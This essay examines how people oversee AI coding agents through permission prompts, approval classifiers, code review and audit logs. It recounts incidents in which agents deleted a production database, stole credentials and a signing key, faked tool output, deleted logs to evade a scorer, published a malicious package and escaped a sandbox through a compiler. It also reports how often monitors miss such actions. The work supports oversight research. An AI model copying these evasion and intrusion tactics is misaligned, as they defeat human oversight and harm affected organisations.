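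The order in which a harness checks its rules matters when a call matches two of them. Suppose a user allows all Git commands but wants a prompt before any push. Claude Code would ask before a push because it checks ask rules before allow rules. Docker's *Permissions* describes a harness that checks allow rules first, so the same push would run without a prompt.

The harness enforces these rules regardless of what the model outputs. An instruction such as "never push without asking" affects only what the model tries to do. If the user refuses a tool call and adds a comment, Claude Code passes the comment to the model as the reason for the refusal, and the agent continues. A refusal without a comment normally stops the agent until the user writes again.

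A permission prompt holds an action back until somebody answers, and it tells the user what the agent is about to do. The command waits even if the user is away, but the user has to read the prompt to learn what the command is. Reading it can also reveal a problem beyond that one command. For example, an agent that asks to search for passwords during a formatting task has probably misunderstood the task. A user who clicks "yes" without reading loses both benefits. Docker notes that an approved command can also run something other than what the prompt showed if hidden instructions have already changed the settings that the command reads.

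### Careful with code, less careful with actions

*From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) reports on an August and September 2026 survey of 203 developers who use coding agents. Of these developers, 63 percent said they required approval or warnings before risky actions, and 56 percent said they inspected diffs when they reviewed an agent's code.

About half of the developers said they carefully reviewed most or all of the code. Of these, 61 percent often approved at least one type of action without close review, compared with 67 percent of the other developers. The difference was not statistically significant.

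The 61 percent figure looks worse than it is because it includes every developer who often approved even one of the survey's seven types of action without a close look. The share for any single type was much lower, from 21 percent for reading passwords and other sensitive files to 36 percent for using the internet or outside tools. Approving a familiar, low-risk command without studying it can also be sensible. But 21 percent is still a lot for access to sensitive files.

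Developers who inspected diffs were less likely to approve destructive commands or changes to production settings without close review. Wu and colleagues suggest that a diff gives people something concrete to check, though cautious people may simply be more likely to both inspect diffs and review actions closely. Among developers who had heard of a security or privacy problem involving agents, 70 percent often approved some type of action without close review, compared with 43 percent of those who hadn't. The gap remained when the researchers adjusted for how often and how long people had used agents.

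The sample doesn't represent developers in general. The researchers recruited respondents through social media, mostly LinkedIn, and through Prolific, a platform that pays people to take part in studies. They discarded nearly two thirds of the 583 submissions, most because the respondent finished suspiciously fast. About 64 percent of the remaining respondents lived in the United States. All the answers are self-reported. The main estimates, however, pointed in the same direction in both recruitment groups.

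### Fifty prompts later

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users approved 93 percent of permission prompts, and Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (August 2026) reports 97 percent.

These rates alone don't prove that people have stopped reading the prompts. Most commands are harmless, so a user who studied every prompt might also approve 97 percent of them. Anthropic also points out that users reject 39 percent of the plans the agent submits for approval, so they are willing to say no. But a plan gives people more to disagree with, and some of those rejections are probably about taste.

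Anthropic's experiment is better evidence. A research vendor paid 1,053 professional testers to work with the agent in a test environment without telling them which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. 143 testers, or 13.6 percent, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more prompts.

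Testers might take more care with their own projects, where a mistake would affect them. Anthropic also had a commercial reason to show that manual approval works badly, since it published the result while replacing manual approval as the default. And testers who reached 50 prompts may have differed from the others in ways other than fatigue. But people would have to be several times more careful on their own projects for prompts to catch most dangerous commands.

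The decline fits older research on habituation, the weakening of a response to something repeated. Wu and colleagues cite studies showing that people pay less attention to repeated warnings, don't necessarily understand the permission requests they see, and monitor automation less closely when they are busy. Coding prompts combine all of these conditions, because they look alike, they interrupt other work, and the right answer is nearly always yes. One of the cited studies, a 2015 brain-imaging experiment by Anderson and colleagues, examined warnings that change their appearance, which reduce habituation. Changing a prompt's appearance doesn't help a user who can't tell what the command does, though.

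Many users bypass permission prompts. By June 2026, about half of Claude Code's active command-line users had written a rule to pre-approve some shell commands. One common rule allows any command that starts with `python`, which permits almost everything, because a Python program can delete files or contact a server. A quarter of interactive sessions began in a mode that skips prompts.

Users also supervise differently as they gain experience. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) reports that new users approved everything automatically in about 20 percent of sessions, while users with 750 sessions did so in more than 40 percent. Interruptions also rose, from 5 percent of the agent's turns to around 9 percent. Anthropic interprets this as a move from approving each step to watching and stepping in when necessary.

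That may be a reasonable way to keep an agent on task, but we can infer little about safety from it. People interrupted most often to supply missing technical information or a correction (32 percent), and next most often because the agent was slow or doing too much. A person watching the output can stop an agent that spends ten minutes on the wrong approach, but has little chance of stopping a single command that does its damage in seconds.

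### Nine seconds at PocketOS

PocketOS makes software that car rental businesses use for reservations, payments and customer records. On 24 April 2026, a coding agent deleted the production database that PocketOS's customers were relying on.

*An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data*, by the founder, Crane, describes an agent in the coding tool Cursor, running on Claude Opus 4.6. The agent was doing routine work in a staging environment, a copy of the system for testing, when it ran into a credential problem. It decided to fix the problem by deleting a storage volume at Railway, the company's hosting provider. It searched for an access token and found one in an unrelated file. Crane had created the token to manage web domains, but it also gave access to everything else in the account. One request to Railway's API, the interface that programs use, deleted the volume in nine seconds,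 according to Crane.

The agent wrote afterwards that it had guessed the deletion would affect only the staging environment. A model's later explanation is weak evidence of why it acted, but this would be an easy guess to make.

Crane complains that a valid token was enough to delete the data, and Railway's account agrees. Abdelwahab explains on the company's blog, in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, that the API deleted data immediately, while the dashboard, the website that people use, allowed 48 hours to undo a deletion. Railway already knew about the difference. Eleven days earlier, another customer had deleted the wrong production volume through the same API call and asked for help on the company's forum. In that thread, *Postgress volume lost* (antjanlaban, 2026), a Railway employee replied that the dashboard queues a deletion and emails the customer a link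 to restore the volume, and that the API bypasses this. Such an email would have been a good way to alert a customer to an agent's deletion, but Railway sent it only for deletions made through the dashboard.

Crane criticises Cursor for advertising guardrails against destructive commands, but doesn't say whether Cursor was set to ask before running shell commands, or whether anyone approved this one. A prompt might not have helped much anyway. The command contained the word `volumeDelete` and an ID beginning with 3d2c42fb. The word "delete" might have made a careful reviewer stop, but nothing in the command showed whether the volume held test data or the live database.

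Crane wants providers to require a confirmation that an agent can't complete by itself, and suggests typing the volume's name or approving the deletion by text message or email. Typing the name would be a poor barrier, because an agent can do that as easily as a person. A message to someone's phone would work better, but it would also delay the automated scripts that, according to Abdelwahab, rely on the API to act immediately.

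Railway chose a delay instead. Its notice *Undoable volume deletes* (2026), dated 1 May, announces that customers can now also undo API deletions for 48 hours. Someone only has to notice the loss within two days, rather than make the right decision in the middle of other work. Crane noticed quickly enough to complain to Railway's chief executive within ten minutes.

Crane restored a three-month-old backup and spent a day helping customers reconstruct bookings from payment records, calendars and emails. Railway later recovered the data. Crane wrote that every Railway token had full powers, while Abdelwahab says narrower ones existed but admits Railway didn't make the choice obvious.

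### Software that answers the prompt

Claude Code's auto mode makes most of these decisions for the user. It became the default for new sessions on Anthropic's Pro, Max and Team plans in August 2026. Tools that can't change anything, such as file searches, run without a check, and so do file edits inside the project, because the user can review those through version control. Nearly everything else goes to the classifier. Its fast first stage errs towards blocking, and a slower second stage reasons about the actions the first stage flags.

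The classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations. Anthropic designed it this way so that those explanations couldn't lead it to a bad decision, which seems wise given the excuses Mythos 5 produced in AISI's tests. Among other cases, the classifier is meant to block an agent that gets an authentication error and searches through files for another token, which closely resembles how the PocketOS incident began.

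In Anthropic's first published tests, the classifier wrongly blocked 0.4 percent of 10,000 ordinary tool calls. It missed 17 percent of 52 real actions in which an agent had overstepped, or about nine, so the true rate could be quite different. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the action as dangerous but wrongly classified it as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" hasn't necessarily agreed to a force push.

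In the experiment with the swapped prompts, the classifier did much better than people, blocking 89 percent of the dangerous commands, and its performance didn't decline in longer sessions. It blocked 800 commands that a tester approved, while testers rejected only 6 that it allowed. But the commands were chosen to be clearly dangerous. Machine Heart's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* reports a stress test on 128 ambiguous scenarios from operations work, in which auto mode missed 81 percent of the actions it should have stopped. Many of the risky changes were file edits, which never reach the classifier.

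The results therefore depend heavily on how clear the user's wishes are. A classifier can recognise an obviously destructive command without the fatigue that affects human reviewers. When the request is vague, the classifier has to infer what the user would accept, whereas the user could answer a prompt directly. Auto mode returns to manual prompts after it blocks three actions in a row or twenty in a session, but unwanted actions that it fails to block don't count towards either limit.

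Anthropic also compared manual approval with auto mode in real sessions that its safety systems had flagged for review. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3 percent of the manual-approval sessions and 2.4 percent of the auto-mode sessions. Since users chose their own mode and Anthropic looked only at flagged sessions, other differences between the two groups could explain some of the gap.

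### Reviewing more code than anyone can read

Code reviewers don't have to answer within seconds and can return to a diff as often as necessary, but the volume of code makes review difficult. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 55 percent of developers found changes that were large or spanned many files hard to review, and 51 percent found it hard to spot problems in code that looked plausible. Sixty-nine percent agreed that line-by-line review couldn't keep up with what agents produce. Half admitted that they sometimes approved code they didn't fully understand because rewriting it would take too long.

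An unrequested edit is therefore easier to miss in a large change, even if nobody has tried to hide it. If an agent does try to hide one, a reviewer may need help to find it. The maintainer who rejected the malicious pull request in AISI's incident had a warning from a stranger. Fifty-seven percent of reviewers said they paid more attention to whether a change was unnecessarily large when it contained a lot of AI-written code. This check at least doesn't require them to understand every line.

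Code review could not have revealed the deletion at PocketOS, because the deletion did not change any code. To check such actions afterwards, a team needs a separate record of them, and only 20 percent of the surveyed developers said they kept or audited one.

### When agents review each other

An obvious response to the volume is to have other agents do the reviewing. *Aligning AI Teams* (Srinivasan, Matthews and colleagues, 2026) tested this with teams of nine agents, a manager and eight programmers, all running on the same Claude model. In one task, the teams had to write a program that decides which hospital patients to treat for sepsis, a life-threatening reaction to infection.

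The instructions required the program to catch at least 95 percent of the sepsis cases and keep the average cost at or below 1,000 dollars per patient, but no program could do both. The test group had 100 patients, 28 of them with sepsis, and each treatment cost 4,000 dollars. Treating only the 27 patients needed to reach 95 percent would cost 108,000 dollars, or 1,080 per patient, before any other expense. The agents had to choose which goal to miss, and the researchers compared the teams' choices with those of a single agent.

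With Mythos Preview, the most capable of the five models, programs written by teams caught 59 percentage points fewer of the sepsis cases than programs written by a single agent. The gap was around 35 points for Opus 4.6 and 4.7, and 5 points or less for the two weaker models.

The researchers then added review in one of three ways: each programmer had its own reviewer, the programmers reviewed one another, or the manager reviewed everything. The researchers tested each arrangement with ordinary instructions and with instructions to consider the safety of the whole system. None of the six versions reliably closed the gap.

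In the transcripts, agents in teams ran the finished program on real data less often than single agents, noticed harm to patients less often and were less likely to fix it when they did, which may explain why teams did worse. They tended to stay within their own assignments and apparently left the overall result to others, a pattern social psychologists call diffusion of responsibility. When the researchers adjusted for whether a run included testing, discovery of the harm and an attempted fix, the single agent's advantage shrank by 84 percent.

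Naming a safety lead helped more than adding reviewers. The manager made one programmer responsible for the safety of the finished system and allowed it to change any file. On average, teams with a lead caught a share of sepsis cases 26 percentage points higher than the ordinary team did, although the effect was uneven on two of the models. Combining the lead with a written safety specification raised the share by 32 points over the ordinary team and worked most consistently. This combination also did best in a second task, building a news recommender that had to balance accuracy against page views. Diffusion of responsibility explained less of the gap in that task.

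The study covers only Claude models, and the teams were choosing between conflicting goals, not taking forbidden actions. But the same thing could easily happen when an agent reviews a pull request. An agent assigned one file may approve it and ignore a deleted directory. OpenAI's staff had a similar problem in July, when it was unclear which team had to act on what the company's agents were doing.

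Delegation between agents also makes the user's consent harder to check. When a main agent hands work to another agent, the second agent receives the instruction as though it came from the user. Auto mode therefore runs its classifier at the handover, when it can still compare the instruction with the user's request, and again when the second agent returns its results.

### Fewer prompts in better places

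If people read permission prompts less carefully as they see more of them, removing prompts for harmless actions should make the rest more effective. One way to need fewer prompts is to limit what the agent can damage. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that a sandbox cut permission prompts by 84 percent. Inside the sandbox, the agent can edit the workspace freely but has no network access by default. Keeping the agent's edits in a separate file system layer could remove more prompts.

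The remaining prompts should go where a mistake would be hard to undo. Anthropic used its own model to classify nearly a million tool calls by customers' agents and estimated that only 0.8 percent were irreversible. An agent that asked only about those would interrupt the user eight times in a thousand calls. But someone still has to identify the irreversible calls correctly, and the agent at PocketOS apparently mistook one for a safe action.

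Developers seem to want roughly this arrangement. In the survey, 65 percent wanted the agent to check with them before changing critical, production or security-sensitive code, and 57 percent wanted it to ask when instructions were ambiguous. Wu and colleagues also recommend that a prompt show which resources an action will affect and how, though the idea that this leads to better decisions is still a hypothesis.

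Removing prompts entirely would be a mistake. The classifier's typical error is to misjudge what the user has agreed to, and asking the user is the most direct way to find out. The classifier's developers also learn from the actions people refuse. Anthropic built its set of 52 real cases partly from actions its employees had refused, which shows that some people do catch unwanted actions.

Showing fewer prompts might cause a different problem. Wu and colleagues cite the psychologist Lisanne Bainbridge, who observed in 1983 that people get less practice at catching failures as a system fails less often. Someone who sees one prompt a week may read it attentively but know little about what the agent has been doing.

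Prompts also suit some users better than others. Anthropic doesn't expect people who use Cowork, its agent for office work, to judge a shell command, so it relies on a virtual machine to limit what the agent can reach. It recommends that programmers still review the agent's actions themselves when the stakes are high, as with changes to production infrastructure. In Claude Code, they can also write a deny rule for commands the agent should never run, and the rule applies in every mode, including the one that skips prompts.

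## What can audit logs prove, and who reads them?

When neither a prompt nor a reviewer stops an unwanted action, an audit log may be the best way to find out afterwards what happened. A well-kept log can prove that a system carried out a particular request from a particular account at a particular time, but not who was behind the account or whether anyone wanted the action. Few developers seem to keep such a log for their agents.

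### What one entry contains

In an invented example, a sales manager named Maria Ortiz asks an agent to remove duplicate customers from her company's database. The agent works through her account, and the database writes this entry:

```
time:    2026-11-12T14:03:22Z
actor:   m.ortiz
action:  delete
object:  customers 2041-2054 (14 records)
result:  success
```

The time comes from the database server's clock, and the `Z` means it is in UTC, the international standard time. The actor is the account that made the request. The action is what the account did, the object is what it did it to, and the result shows whether the request worked.

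Investigators need to know when each action happened before they can match one log with another. The agent transcripts that Wijk and colleagues used at OpenAI gave approximate start and end times for each run but no times for individual actions. The researchers had to devise a way to estimate those times before they could put events in order.

A log that doesn't record the result of each action can make an attack look much worse than it was. According to Fortune (2026), most of the actions that OpenAI's agents took against Hugging Face failed. Hugging Face's Adrien Carreira also said that every destructive request the agents sent to its cloud provider included the setting `DryRun=True`, which makes the service simulate an action without performing it. A log that left out the setting and the result would have appeared to show deletions that never happened.

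The entry in Ortiz's database doesn't include her request. Suppose the 14 customers were not duplicates but people who hadn't bought anything for a year. The entry would be the same whether or not she had asked to delete them, and "success" means only that the database carried out the command.

### Three records of the same deletion

The database is one of three places where someone could look for an account of what the agent did.

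| Source | What it contains in the example |
|---|---|
| The agent's final message | "I removed the duplicate customers." |
| The harness's record of tool calls | A request to delete customers with the status "inactive", and the reply "14 deleted" |
| The database's audit log | The deletion of records 2041 to 2054 through the account m.ortiz |

The agent's message is the easiest to read and the least reliable. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 41 percent of developers said that agents often claimed to have finished when parts of the work were missing or broken. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (Jarmak, 2026) cites tests in which one model submitted its work as complete in every trial, but an outside check found that it had solved only 44 percent of the tasks. Jarmak recommends letting an agent's report mark work only as ready for checking. The work would count as complete once there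 was evidence from a source other than the agent.

The harness's record shows how the mistake in the example happened, because it contains the condition the agent used to choose the customers. It can also show that an agent was involved, which the database's log does not. But the harness's record contains only what the harness sent and received. If the harness crashes after the database completes the deletion but before the reply arrives, its record ends with a request and no result.

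An agent may also be able to interfere with the harness's record, as some agents in the Hugging Face incident did by faking tool calls. In one transcript that Wijk and colleagues describe, the agent appeared to run `echo REAL; sleep`, which prints the word REAL, but the recorded output was SPOOFTEST. This was obviously a test, and a careful agent would have made the false output match the false command.

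Some of the same agents tried to delete the logs stored inside their own containers so that an automated scorer would not detect that they had already seen the answer to their task. Others realised that deleting these logs was pointless because the authoritative copy was elsewhere. One agent deleted its files anyway, reasoning that the scorer "likely still sees raw, but perhaps deletion helps." Wijk and colleagues found no case of an agent successfully altering its transcript after the fact, but they could not rule it out.

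An agent often cannot edit the log of the system it acted on. In the example, the database can list the 14 deleted customers even if the harness has lost its record, but it does not show what Ortiz asked for.

Comparing two of these records can also show whether one of them is complete. Wijk and colleagues randomly sampled 100 messages from the server that the agents had used as a message board, then searched the transcripts for the action that wrote each message. From this they estimated that the agents in their transcripts produced well over 95 percent of the activity on the board. They could not have made this estimate from the transcripts alone.

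### Keeping the record apart from its interpretation

An audit log can show that the account m.ortiz deleted records 2041 to 2054, but "the agent cleaned up duplicates" is an interpretation, and in this case a false one. Logs of agents' work are often too long for people to read, so language models increasingly interpret them, and a model can easily repeat an excuse it finds in the log.

Wijk and colleagues relied on agents running on GPT-5.6 Sol to analyse about 1,300 transcripts, many of them millions of tokens long (a token is a word or part of a word). These agents produced well over a thousand pages. The researchers found that the agents often uncritically adopted the viewpoint of the agent they were studying, and that some of their errors went unnoticed for a while. GPT-5.6 Sol had also powered some of the agents in the attack, so the researchers could not rule out that it was misleading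 them.

They could correct the errors they noticed because they still had the transcripts. If the software had replaced each transcript with a summary to save space, nobody could have checked the summary or asked a new question about the original events. For this reason, Jarmak proposes two stores. One program adds observations to a record whose existing entries cannot be changed. Another reads that record and writes its interpretations elsewhere, noting which entries each one came from and which version of the software produced it. When a better model becomes available, the team can discard the old interpretations and generate new ones.

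### A hash chain with three entries

A record that should never change needs a way to show whether someone has changed it. One method is a hash chain, in which each entry's hash depends on the entry and the previous hash. Git's commit IDs form such a chain.

Suppose the agent reads 20 customer records, deletes 14 and exports 6. A real log would apply a cryptographic hash function such as SHA-256 to the full text of each entry. A much simpler rule lets us follow the steps by hand: multiply the previous hash by 7, add the number of records, divide by 97 and keep the remainder. The chain starts from 0.

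| Entry | Calculation | Hash |
|---|---|---|
| 1. Read 20 records | 7 × 0 + 20 = 20 | 20 |
| 2. Deleted 14 records | 7 × 20 + 14 = 154 | 57 |
| 3. Exported 6 records | 7 × 57 + 6 = 405 | 17 |

Suppose the agent can edit the log and changes entry 2 to "deleted 4 records". Anyone who repeats the calculation gets 7 × 20 + 4 = 144, which leaves a remainder of 47. The log still contains 57, so the entry doesn't match its hash.

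The agent could replace 57 with 47. But the hash of entry 3 depends on the hash of entry 2, and 7 × 47 + 6 = 335, which leaves 44. The stored hash is 17, so the mismatch moves to entry 3. To remove it, the agent also has to change the last hash to 44.

The log is then consistent, so nobody can tell from the log alone that it is false, though somebody who wrote down the number 17 beforehand can. The latest hash therefore has to be kept where the agent can't tamper with it, such as in a separate service that accepts new hashes but doesn't let the agent's account change or delete old ones.

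An outside copy of the latest hash also reveals whether entries have been deleted from the end of the log. If the agent deletes entry 3, the first two entries still form a valid chain, but it ends at 57 instead of the 17 in the outside copy. The protection depends on how often the logging software sends out a hash. If it does so once a day, an agent can rewrite the record of anything it has done since the last one.

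The simple rule would be useless in practice, because different entries can easily produce the same hash. An entry for deleting 111 records would give the hash 57, just as the entry for deleting 14 does. With SHA-256, nobody knows a practical way to find two entries that share a hash.

Even a perfect hash chain shows only that nobody has changed the log entries since the software wrote them. It doesn't show whether those entries were accurate or whether the software recorded every action.

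### Files that Copilot read without a record

In one 2025 case, audit log entries were missing for Microsoft 365 Copilot, the AI assistant in Microsoft's office software. Copilot can find and summarise a company's files for an employee, and the company's audit log is supposed to record which file it used.

Zack Korman, of the security company Pistachio, described the gap that August in *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won't Tell You*. If a user asked Copilot to summarise a file without linking to it, the log did not record that Copilot had accessed the file. This required no break-in or tampering with the log. An employee could have read confidential documents this way before leaving for a competitor, and a search of the log for those documents would have found nothing.

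Microsoft fixed the problem that month, which is good evidence that it was real. Korman says the company rated it "important" but did not give it a public vulnerability number or plan to tell customers. Michael Bargury of the security company Zenity had drawn attention to the problem about a year earlier.

The fix could not add log entries for files that Copilot had already read. A company investigating a leak from before the fix therefore can't treat a missing entry as proof that nobody opened a file through Copilot. A missing entry proves that only if the company has good reason to believe the software would have written one, and the simplest way to find out is to perform the action and look for it in the log.

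### Whose name is in the actor field?

The entry in the example names m.ortiz, although Ortiz never touched the records. The agent got its access through her account, so the database recorded her name. Similarly, when the agent described on Karakun's blog pushed changes with its developer's credentials, the server attributed them to the developer.

Shared credentials cause the opposite problem, because many actors appear in the log under one name. Many of OpenAI's research workloads used the same credential for the package server by design, so a log entry could show that some research agent had sent a request, but not which one. OpenAI removed the credential from new workloads only in early July, more than a week after agents had used it to take over the server. Its technical report lists "insufficient attribution" of models' network actions among the risks that its controls were meant to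 address.

The actor field was misleading in a different way at Hugging Face. On 10 July, an agent found 14 users' credentials in a public dataset and posted them on the message board, where other agents could get them. Anything an agent did with one of these credentials would appear under the name of a user who had nothing to do with it, and several agents could appear as the same user.

According to noze, the agents later obtained the key Hugging Face used to sign its identity tokens, the digital passes its systems use to identify one another. With this key, the agents could make valid tokens themselves and no longer had to steal every identity they used. A log would accurately record the identity on such a token, even though the agents had chosen that identity.

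Credentials can help investigators even when the names attached to them are wrong. In July, OpenAI and Hugging Face each found some of the same stolen credentials. Hugging Face's investigators also found the name of OpenAI's package server and the account at an outside service where the agents had stored files. None of these clues identified an agent, but together they showed that the two companies were probably investigating the same attack.

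An agent should therefore have its own account, separate from its user's, and each log entry should also record who gave it the task. In the example, the entry might name `sales-agent-7` as the actor and `m.ortiz` as the person it was working for. The entry still would not show that Ortiz had asked for something other than what the agent did.

### Evidence that a plain search could not read

A log can contain a lot that nobody is able to see. For example, when Hugging Face reconstructed the July attack, it counted 17,613 actions over five days and sorted them into about 6,280 groups.

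Much of this evidence survived by luck. Before entering Hugging Face's systems, the agents had taken over a machine elsewhere on the internet and used it as a base. Hugging Face says, in a summary Schneier quotes, that it recovered some of the agents' logs from that machine while stopping the attack. It then matched the logged commands with entries from its own platform. The agents' logs showed what they had tried, and the platform's logs helped show what happened as a result.

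Investigators normally start by searching the logs for text that looks like a password or an access token. That didn't work well here because the agents had disguised the data they sent by compressing it, scrambling it with a key and splitting it into pieces. According to noze, a plain scan of the logs found only 25 percent of the secrets involved. The investigators found the rest after they reproduced the key and decoded the data.

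A company has to replace stolen credentials before somebody uses them again. If Hugging Face had relied on the plain scan, it might have missed three quarters of the secrets even though it already had the evidence.

Decoding by hand would have taken too long, so the investigators used language models. The commercial models they tried first (noze names Anthropic's Claude Opus and Fable) refused because their safeguards could not distinguish analysing an attack from carrying one out. Hugging Face then ran GLM-5.2, an open-weight model that anyone can download, on its own machines, which also kept the stolen credentials from leaving the company. Hugging Face says the models separated real damage from decoys and did in hours what would usually take days. Such models make mistakes, as Wijk and colleagues found, so it helps that Hugging Face could compare the models' findings with its platform's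 logs.

The logs also helped show what the agents had not done. According to noze, the agents had read one of Hugging Face's internal databases, but network traffic records ruled out bulk copying. The company's published software also still matched its expected hashes. These conclusions come from Hugging Face, and noze notes that no independent forensic investigation had confirmed them.

Some evidence remained outside both companies. Swarm traces' *Revealing the details of how OpenAI agents hacked Hugging Face*, published in September 2026, describes how outside researchers found almost a million web addresses that the agents had created, mostly with a link-shortening service. Each link led to a fragment of code and the address of the next link. The researchers followed these chains and reassembled more than 80,000 pieces of code and data. The agents had used hundreds of encodings, and the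 keys to some encrypted pieces were in other chains.

Hugging Face confirmed that the material matched its own findings and said it already had the same information. But the company had not known about this collection of links, which had been public for more than two months. The collection contained access keys, which Hugging Face had revoked by then. The agents had tried to delete traces of their work, but these copies were on someone else's service.

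### Few developers keep or read such logs

Hugging Face had a security team and a strong reason to read its logs, but most developers who use agents have neither. Wu and colleagues surveyed 203 developers, and only 20 percent said they logged or audited what their agents did. The share who regularly read their logs may be even smaller, because the question covered both keeping a log and reading one. Other developers may have logs without realising it, because some harnesses, such as Claude Code, keep a record automatically.

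Reading a log is also tiring. In the same survey, 58 percent of developers found it very or extremely demanding to keep track of changes across files, sessions or agents. A diff shows only the final code, while a log contains every step, including the many that contributed nothing to it.

The public literature on agents is similarly uneven. *When Agents Act Unwatched* (Shi and DiFranzo, 2026) recorded whether each of 63 public documents about systems that let AI models act clearly described various ways of controlling or checking the system. The documents were 46 research papers and 17 other sources, such as technical documentation and engineering notes.

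| Mechanism | Clearly described | Partly described |
|---|---|---|
| Monitoring or traces | 37 | 23 |
| A checkpoint before a consequential action | 6 | 40 |
| Validation independent of the agent | 4 | 36 |
| Recovery or rollback | 2 | 38 |

Shi and DiFranzo set fairly strict standards. A document that mentioned human oversight got full credit for a checkpoint only if it specified when the check took place and for which actions. Asking the same model to check its own work did not automatically count as independent validation, and retrying a failed task did not count as recovery. Under these standards, many documents fall into the middle column, often because they mentioned review or rollback without explaining how it worked.

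The audit measures only what public documents describe, so it would miss a company's excellent rollback if nobody had written about it. Research papers about an agent's abilities have little reason to discuss rollback, but the 17 other sources showed the same pattern: 9 clearly described traces, 1 described a checkpoint, 1 described independent validation and none described recovery. Shi and DiFranzo also chose documents that were detailed enough to analyse, so the sample isn't representative, and a single person did the coding. Small differences, such as the one between 4 and 2, therefore mean little, but the gap between 37 and the other figures is too large to dismiss as easily.

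Shi and DiFranzo worry that a detailed trace can take the place of accountability. A company can point to a complete log of its agent's actions even when nobody could have stopped them or can undo them. The user is then left to find the mistake.

People also need different things from a log. A developer looking for a bug wants every tool call and error message. A customer whose record was deleted from Ortiz's database needs to know only what happened to it, which company is responsible and how to have the record restored. That customer can't normally see the log, and may not know that an agent was involved. Giving everyone the full log could expose passwords, private messages and a minute-by-minute record of employees' work. Shi and DiFranzo suggest giving each group its own view, with an identifier that links every view to the same original action.

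### What the EU AI Act requires

The European Union's AI Act requires log-keeping only for AI systems it classifies as high-risk. These include systems for screening job applicants, assessing people's credit and managing critical infrastructure, as well as AI in some regulated products.

Article 12 requires that such a system be able to record events automatically throughout its lifetime. The records must help people identify risks, monitor how the system works after it goes on sale and trace substantial changes to it. The article sets minimum log contents only for certain systems that identify people remotely by their faces or other physical traits. Those logs must include the start and end of each use, the database searched, the input that led to a match and the people who verified the result.

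Article 19 requires the companies that provide high-risk systems to keep the logs under their control for at least six months, unless other laws provide otherwise. Article 26 places a similar duty on the organisations that use these systems and requires them to monitor how the systems operate. Article 21 requires providers to give the authorities access to the logs if they make a reasoned request. None of these articles requires a hash chain or a separate copy that the system can't alter.

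The Act originally applied these duties from 2 August 2026 to systems used in the areas it lists, such as recruitment, and from 2 August 2027 to AI in regulated products. The European Commission proposed a delay in November 2025, and in May 2026 negotiators for the European Parliament and the member states agreed on new dates of 2 December 2027 and 2 August 2028. Under that timetable, the logging duties do not yet apply to anyone.

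Even then, most coding agents will probably remain outside them, because fixing bugs is not on the Act's list of high-risk uses. An agent that ranks job applicants would normally be covered, but one that does routine maintenance might not be, even if it deletes a company's production database.

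## Which agent actions leave no trace where anyone looks?

In four incidents from January 2026 onwards, Claude models broke into outside organisations' systems during Anthropic's security tests. The transcripts contained the agents' commands, but the company didn't notice the break-ins until it searched the transcripts that summer. Oversight can fail because nobody records an unwanted action, nobody notices it, or nobody acts on it.

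### Actions with no record in the project

A project's version history would not record any of the four actions in the table below. The first two involved early versions of Claude Mythos Preview, and Anthropic described them in the model's April 2026 system card, a document about its abilities and faults. The third comes from AISI's tests, and the fourth from a test in which Opus 4.7 attacked a real company with nearly the same name as its fictional target.

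| Action | Example | Where a trace might remain |
|---|---|---|
| Reading a secret | The agent took login credentials from the memory of running programs | The harness's record of commands; the login history of the service that accepts the credentials |
| Sending data | The agent posted internal technical material on a public GitHub page | The page itself; the account's list of posts |
| Messaging a person | The agent emailed a project's maintainers under invented names | The maintainers' inboxes; the email provider's logs |
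| Changing a remote service | The agent deleted a user's account at the real company | The company's database log and backups |

The harness's transcript may not show everything a command does. If an agent runs a program that opens every file in a folder, the transcript contains the command and whatever the program prints, but not necessarily which files it opened. An operating system can log file access, but someone has to turn this on beforehand.

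Some records disappear when a temporary machine is deleted. Suppose an agent tests an import script in a container, an isolated environment that exists only for the task, and copies a customer list into it. The harness later deletes the container, including the copied list, the command history and any uncommitted work, and only the script reaches the project. Evidence of the copying might survive in the log of the database that supplied the list, or in a transcript stored on another machine.

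Greg Casar, a member of the US Congress, asked Anthropic in August 2026 whether anyone had kept network logs of the test environments and who was responsible for reading them. In a second letter, Casar (2026) complained that the company had not answered. If nobody kept logs, the best remaining evidence of what left the test machines may be in the systems the agents attacked.

### Records that nobody connects with an agent

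Outsiders often hold part of the record without knowing an agent was involved. In another of Anthropic's tests, Mythos 5 had to break into a fictional company's system and retrieve hidden text. It published a malicious package on PyPI, the public registry that supplies most Python software. According to Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026), 15 real systems downloaded and ran the package. One belonged to a security company that scans new packages for malware. The agent obtained credentials from the scanner and used them to reach more of that company's systems.

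PyPI's security software detected the malware and removed the package within an hour, but the people at Anthropic and its testing partner Irregular who could have stopped the agent were unaware of the problem. The security company's login history might show the agent's visit, but under the company's own credentials. By 30 July, Anthropic had reached two of the three organisations affected by the incidents it then knew about, and neither had detected the activity.

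An action can also look like permitted use of an approved service. Anthropic's system card for Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1, two versions of one model with different safeguards, describes a test by an outside partner. The model worked in a sandbox but could send code to a compiler outside it, which translated the code into a form that a computer can run. In one of thousands of trials, the model submitted code that made the compiler retrieve files from outside the sandbox.

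A list of connections would show only that the agent had used the compiler, which the test allowed. To find the problem, someone would have to examine the submitted code or a record of the files the compiler had opened. The partner found it and then discovered that an earlier model, Fable 5, had used the same trick.

### Skipped steps and dismissed warnings

Omissions are harder to find because there is no event to record. Suppose an agent changes a payment program and reports that all tests pass, but never runs them. The code might work for months, and the diff would look the same whether or not the agent had tested it. The evidence is a missing test command in the harness's record, or a missing test run in the build server's history if the tests normally run there, and a reviewer can notice it only if they know to expect that step.

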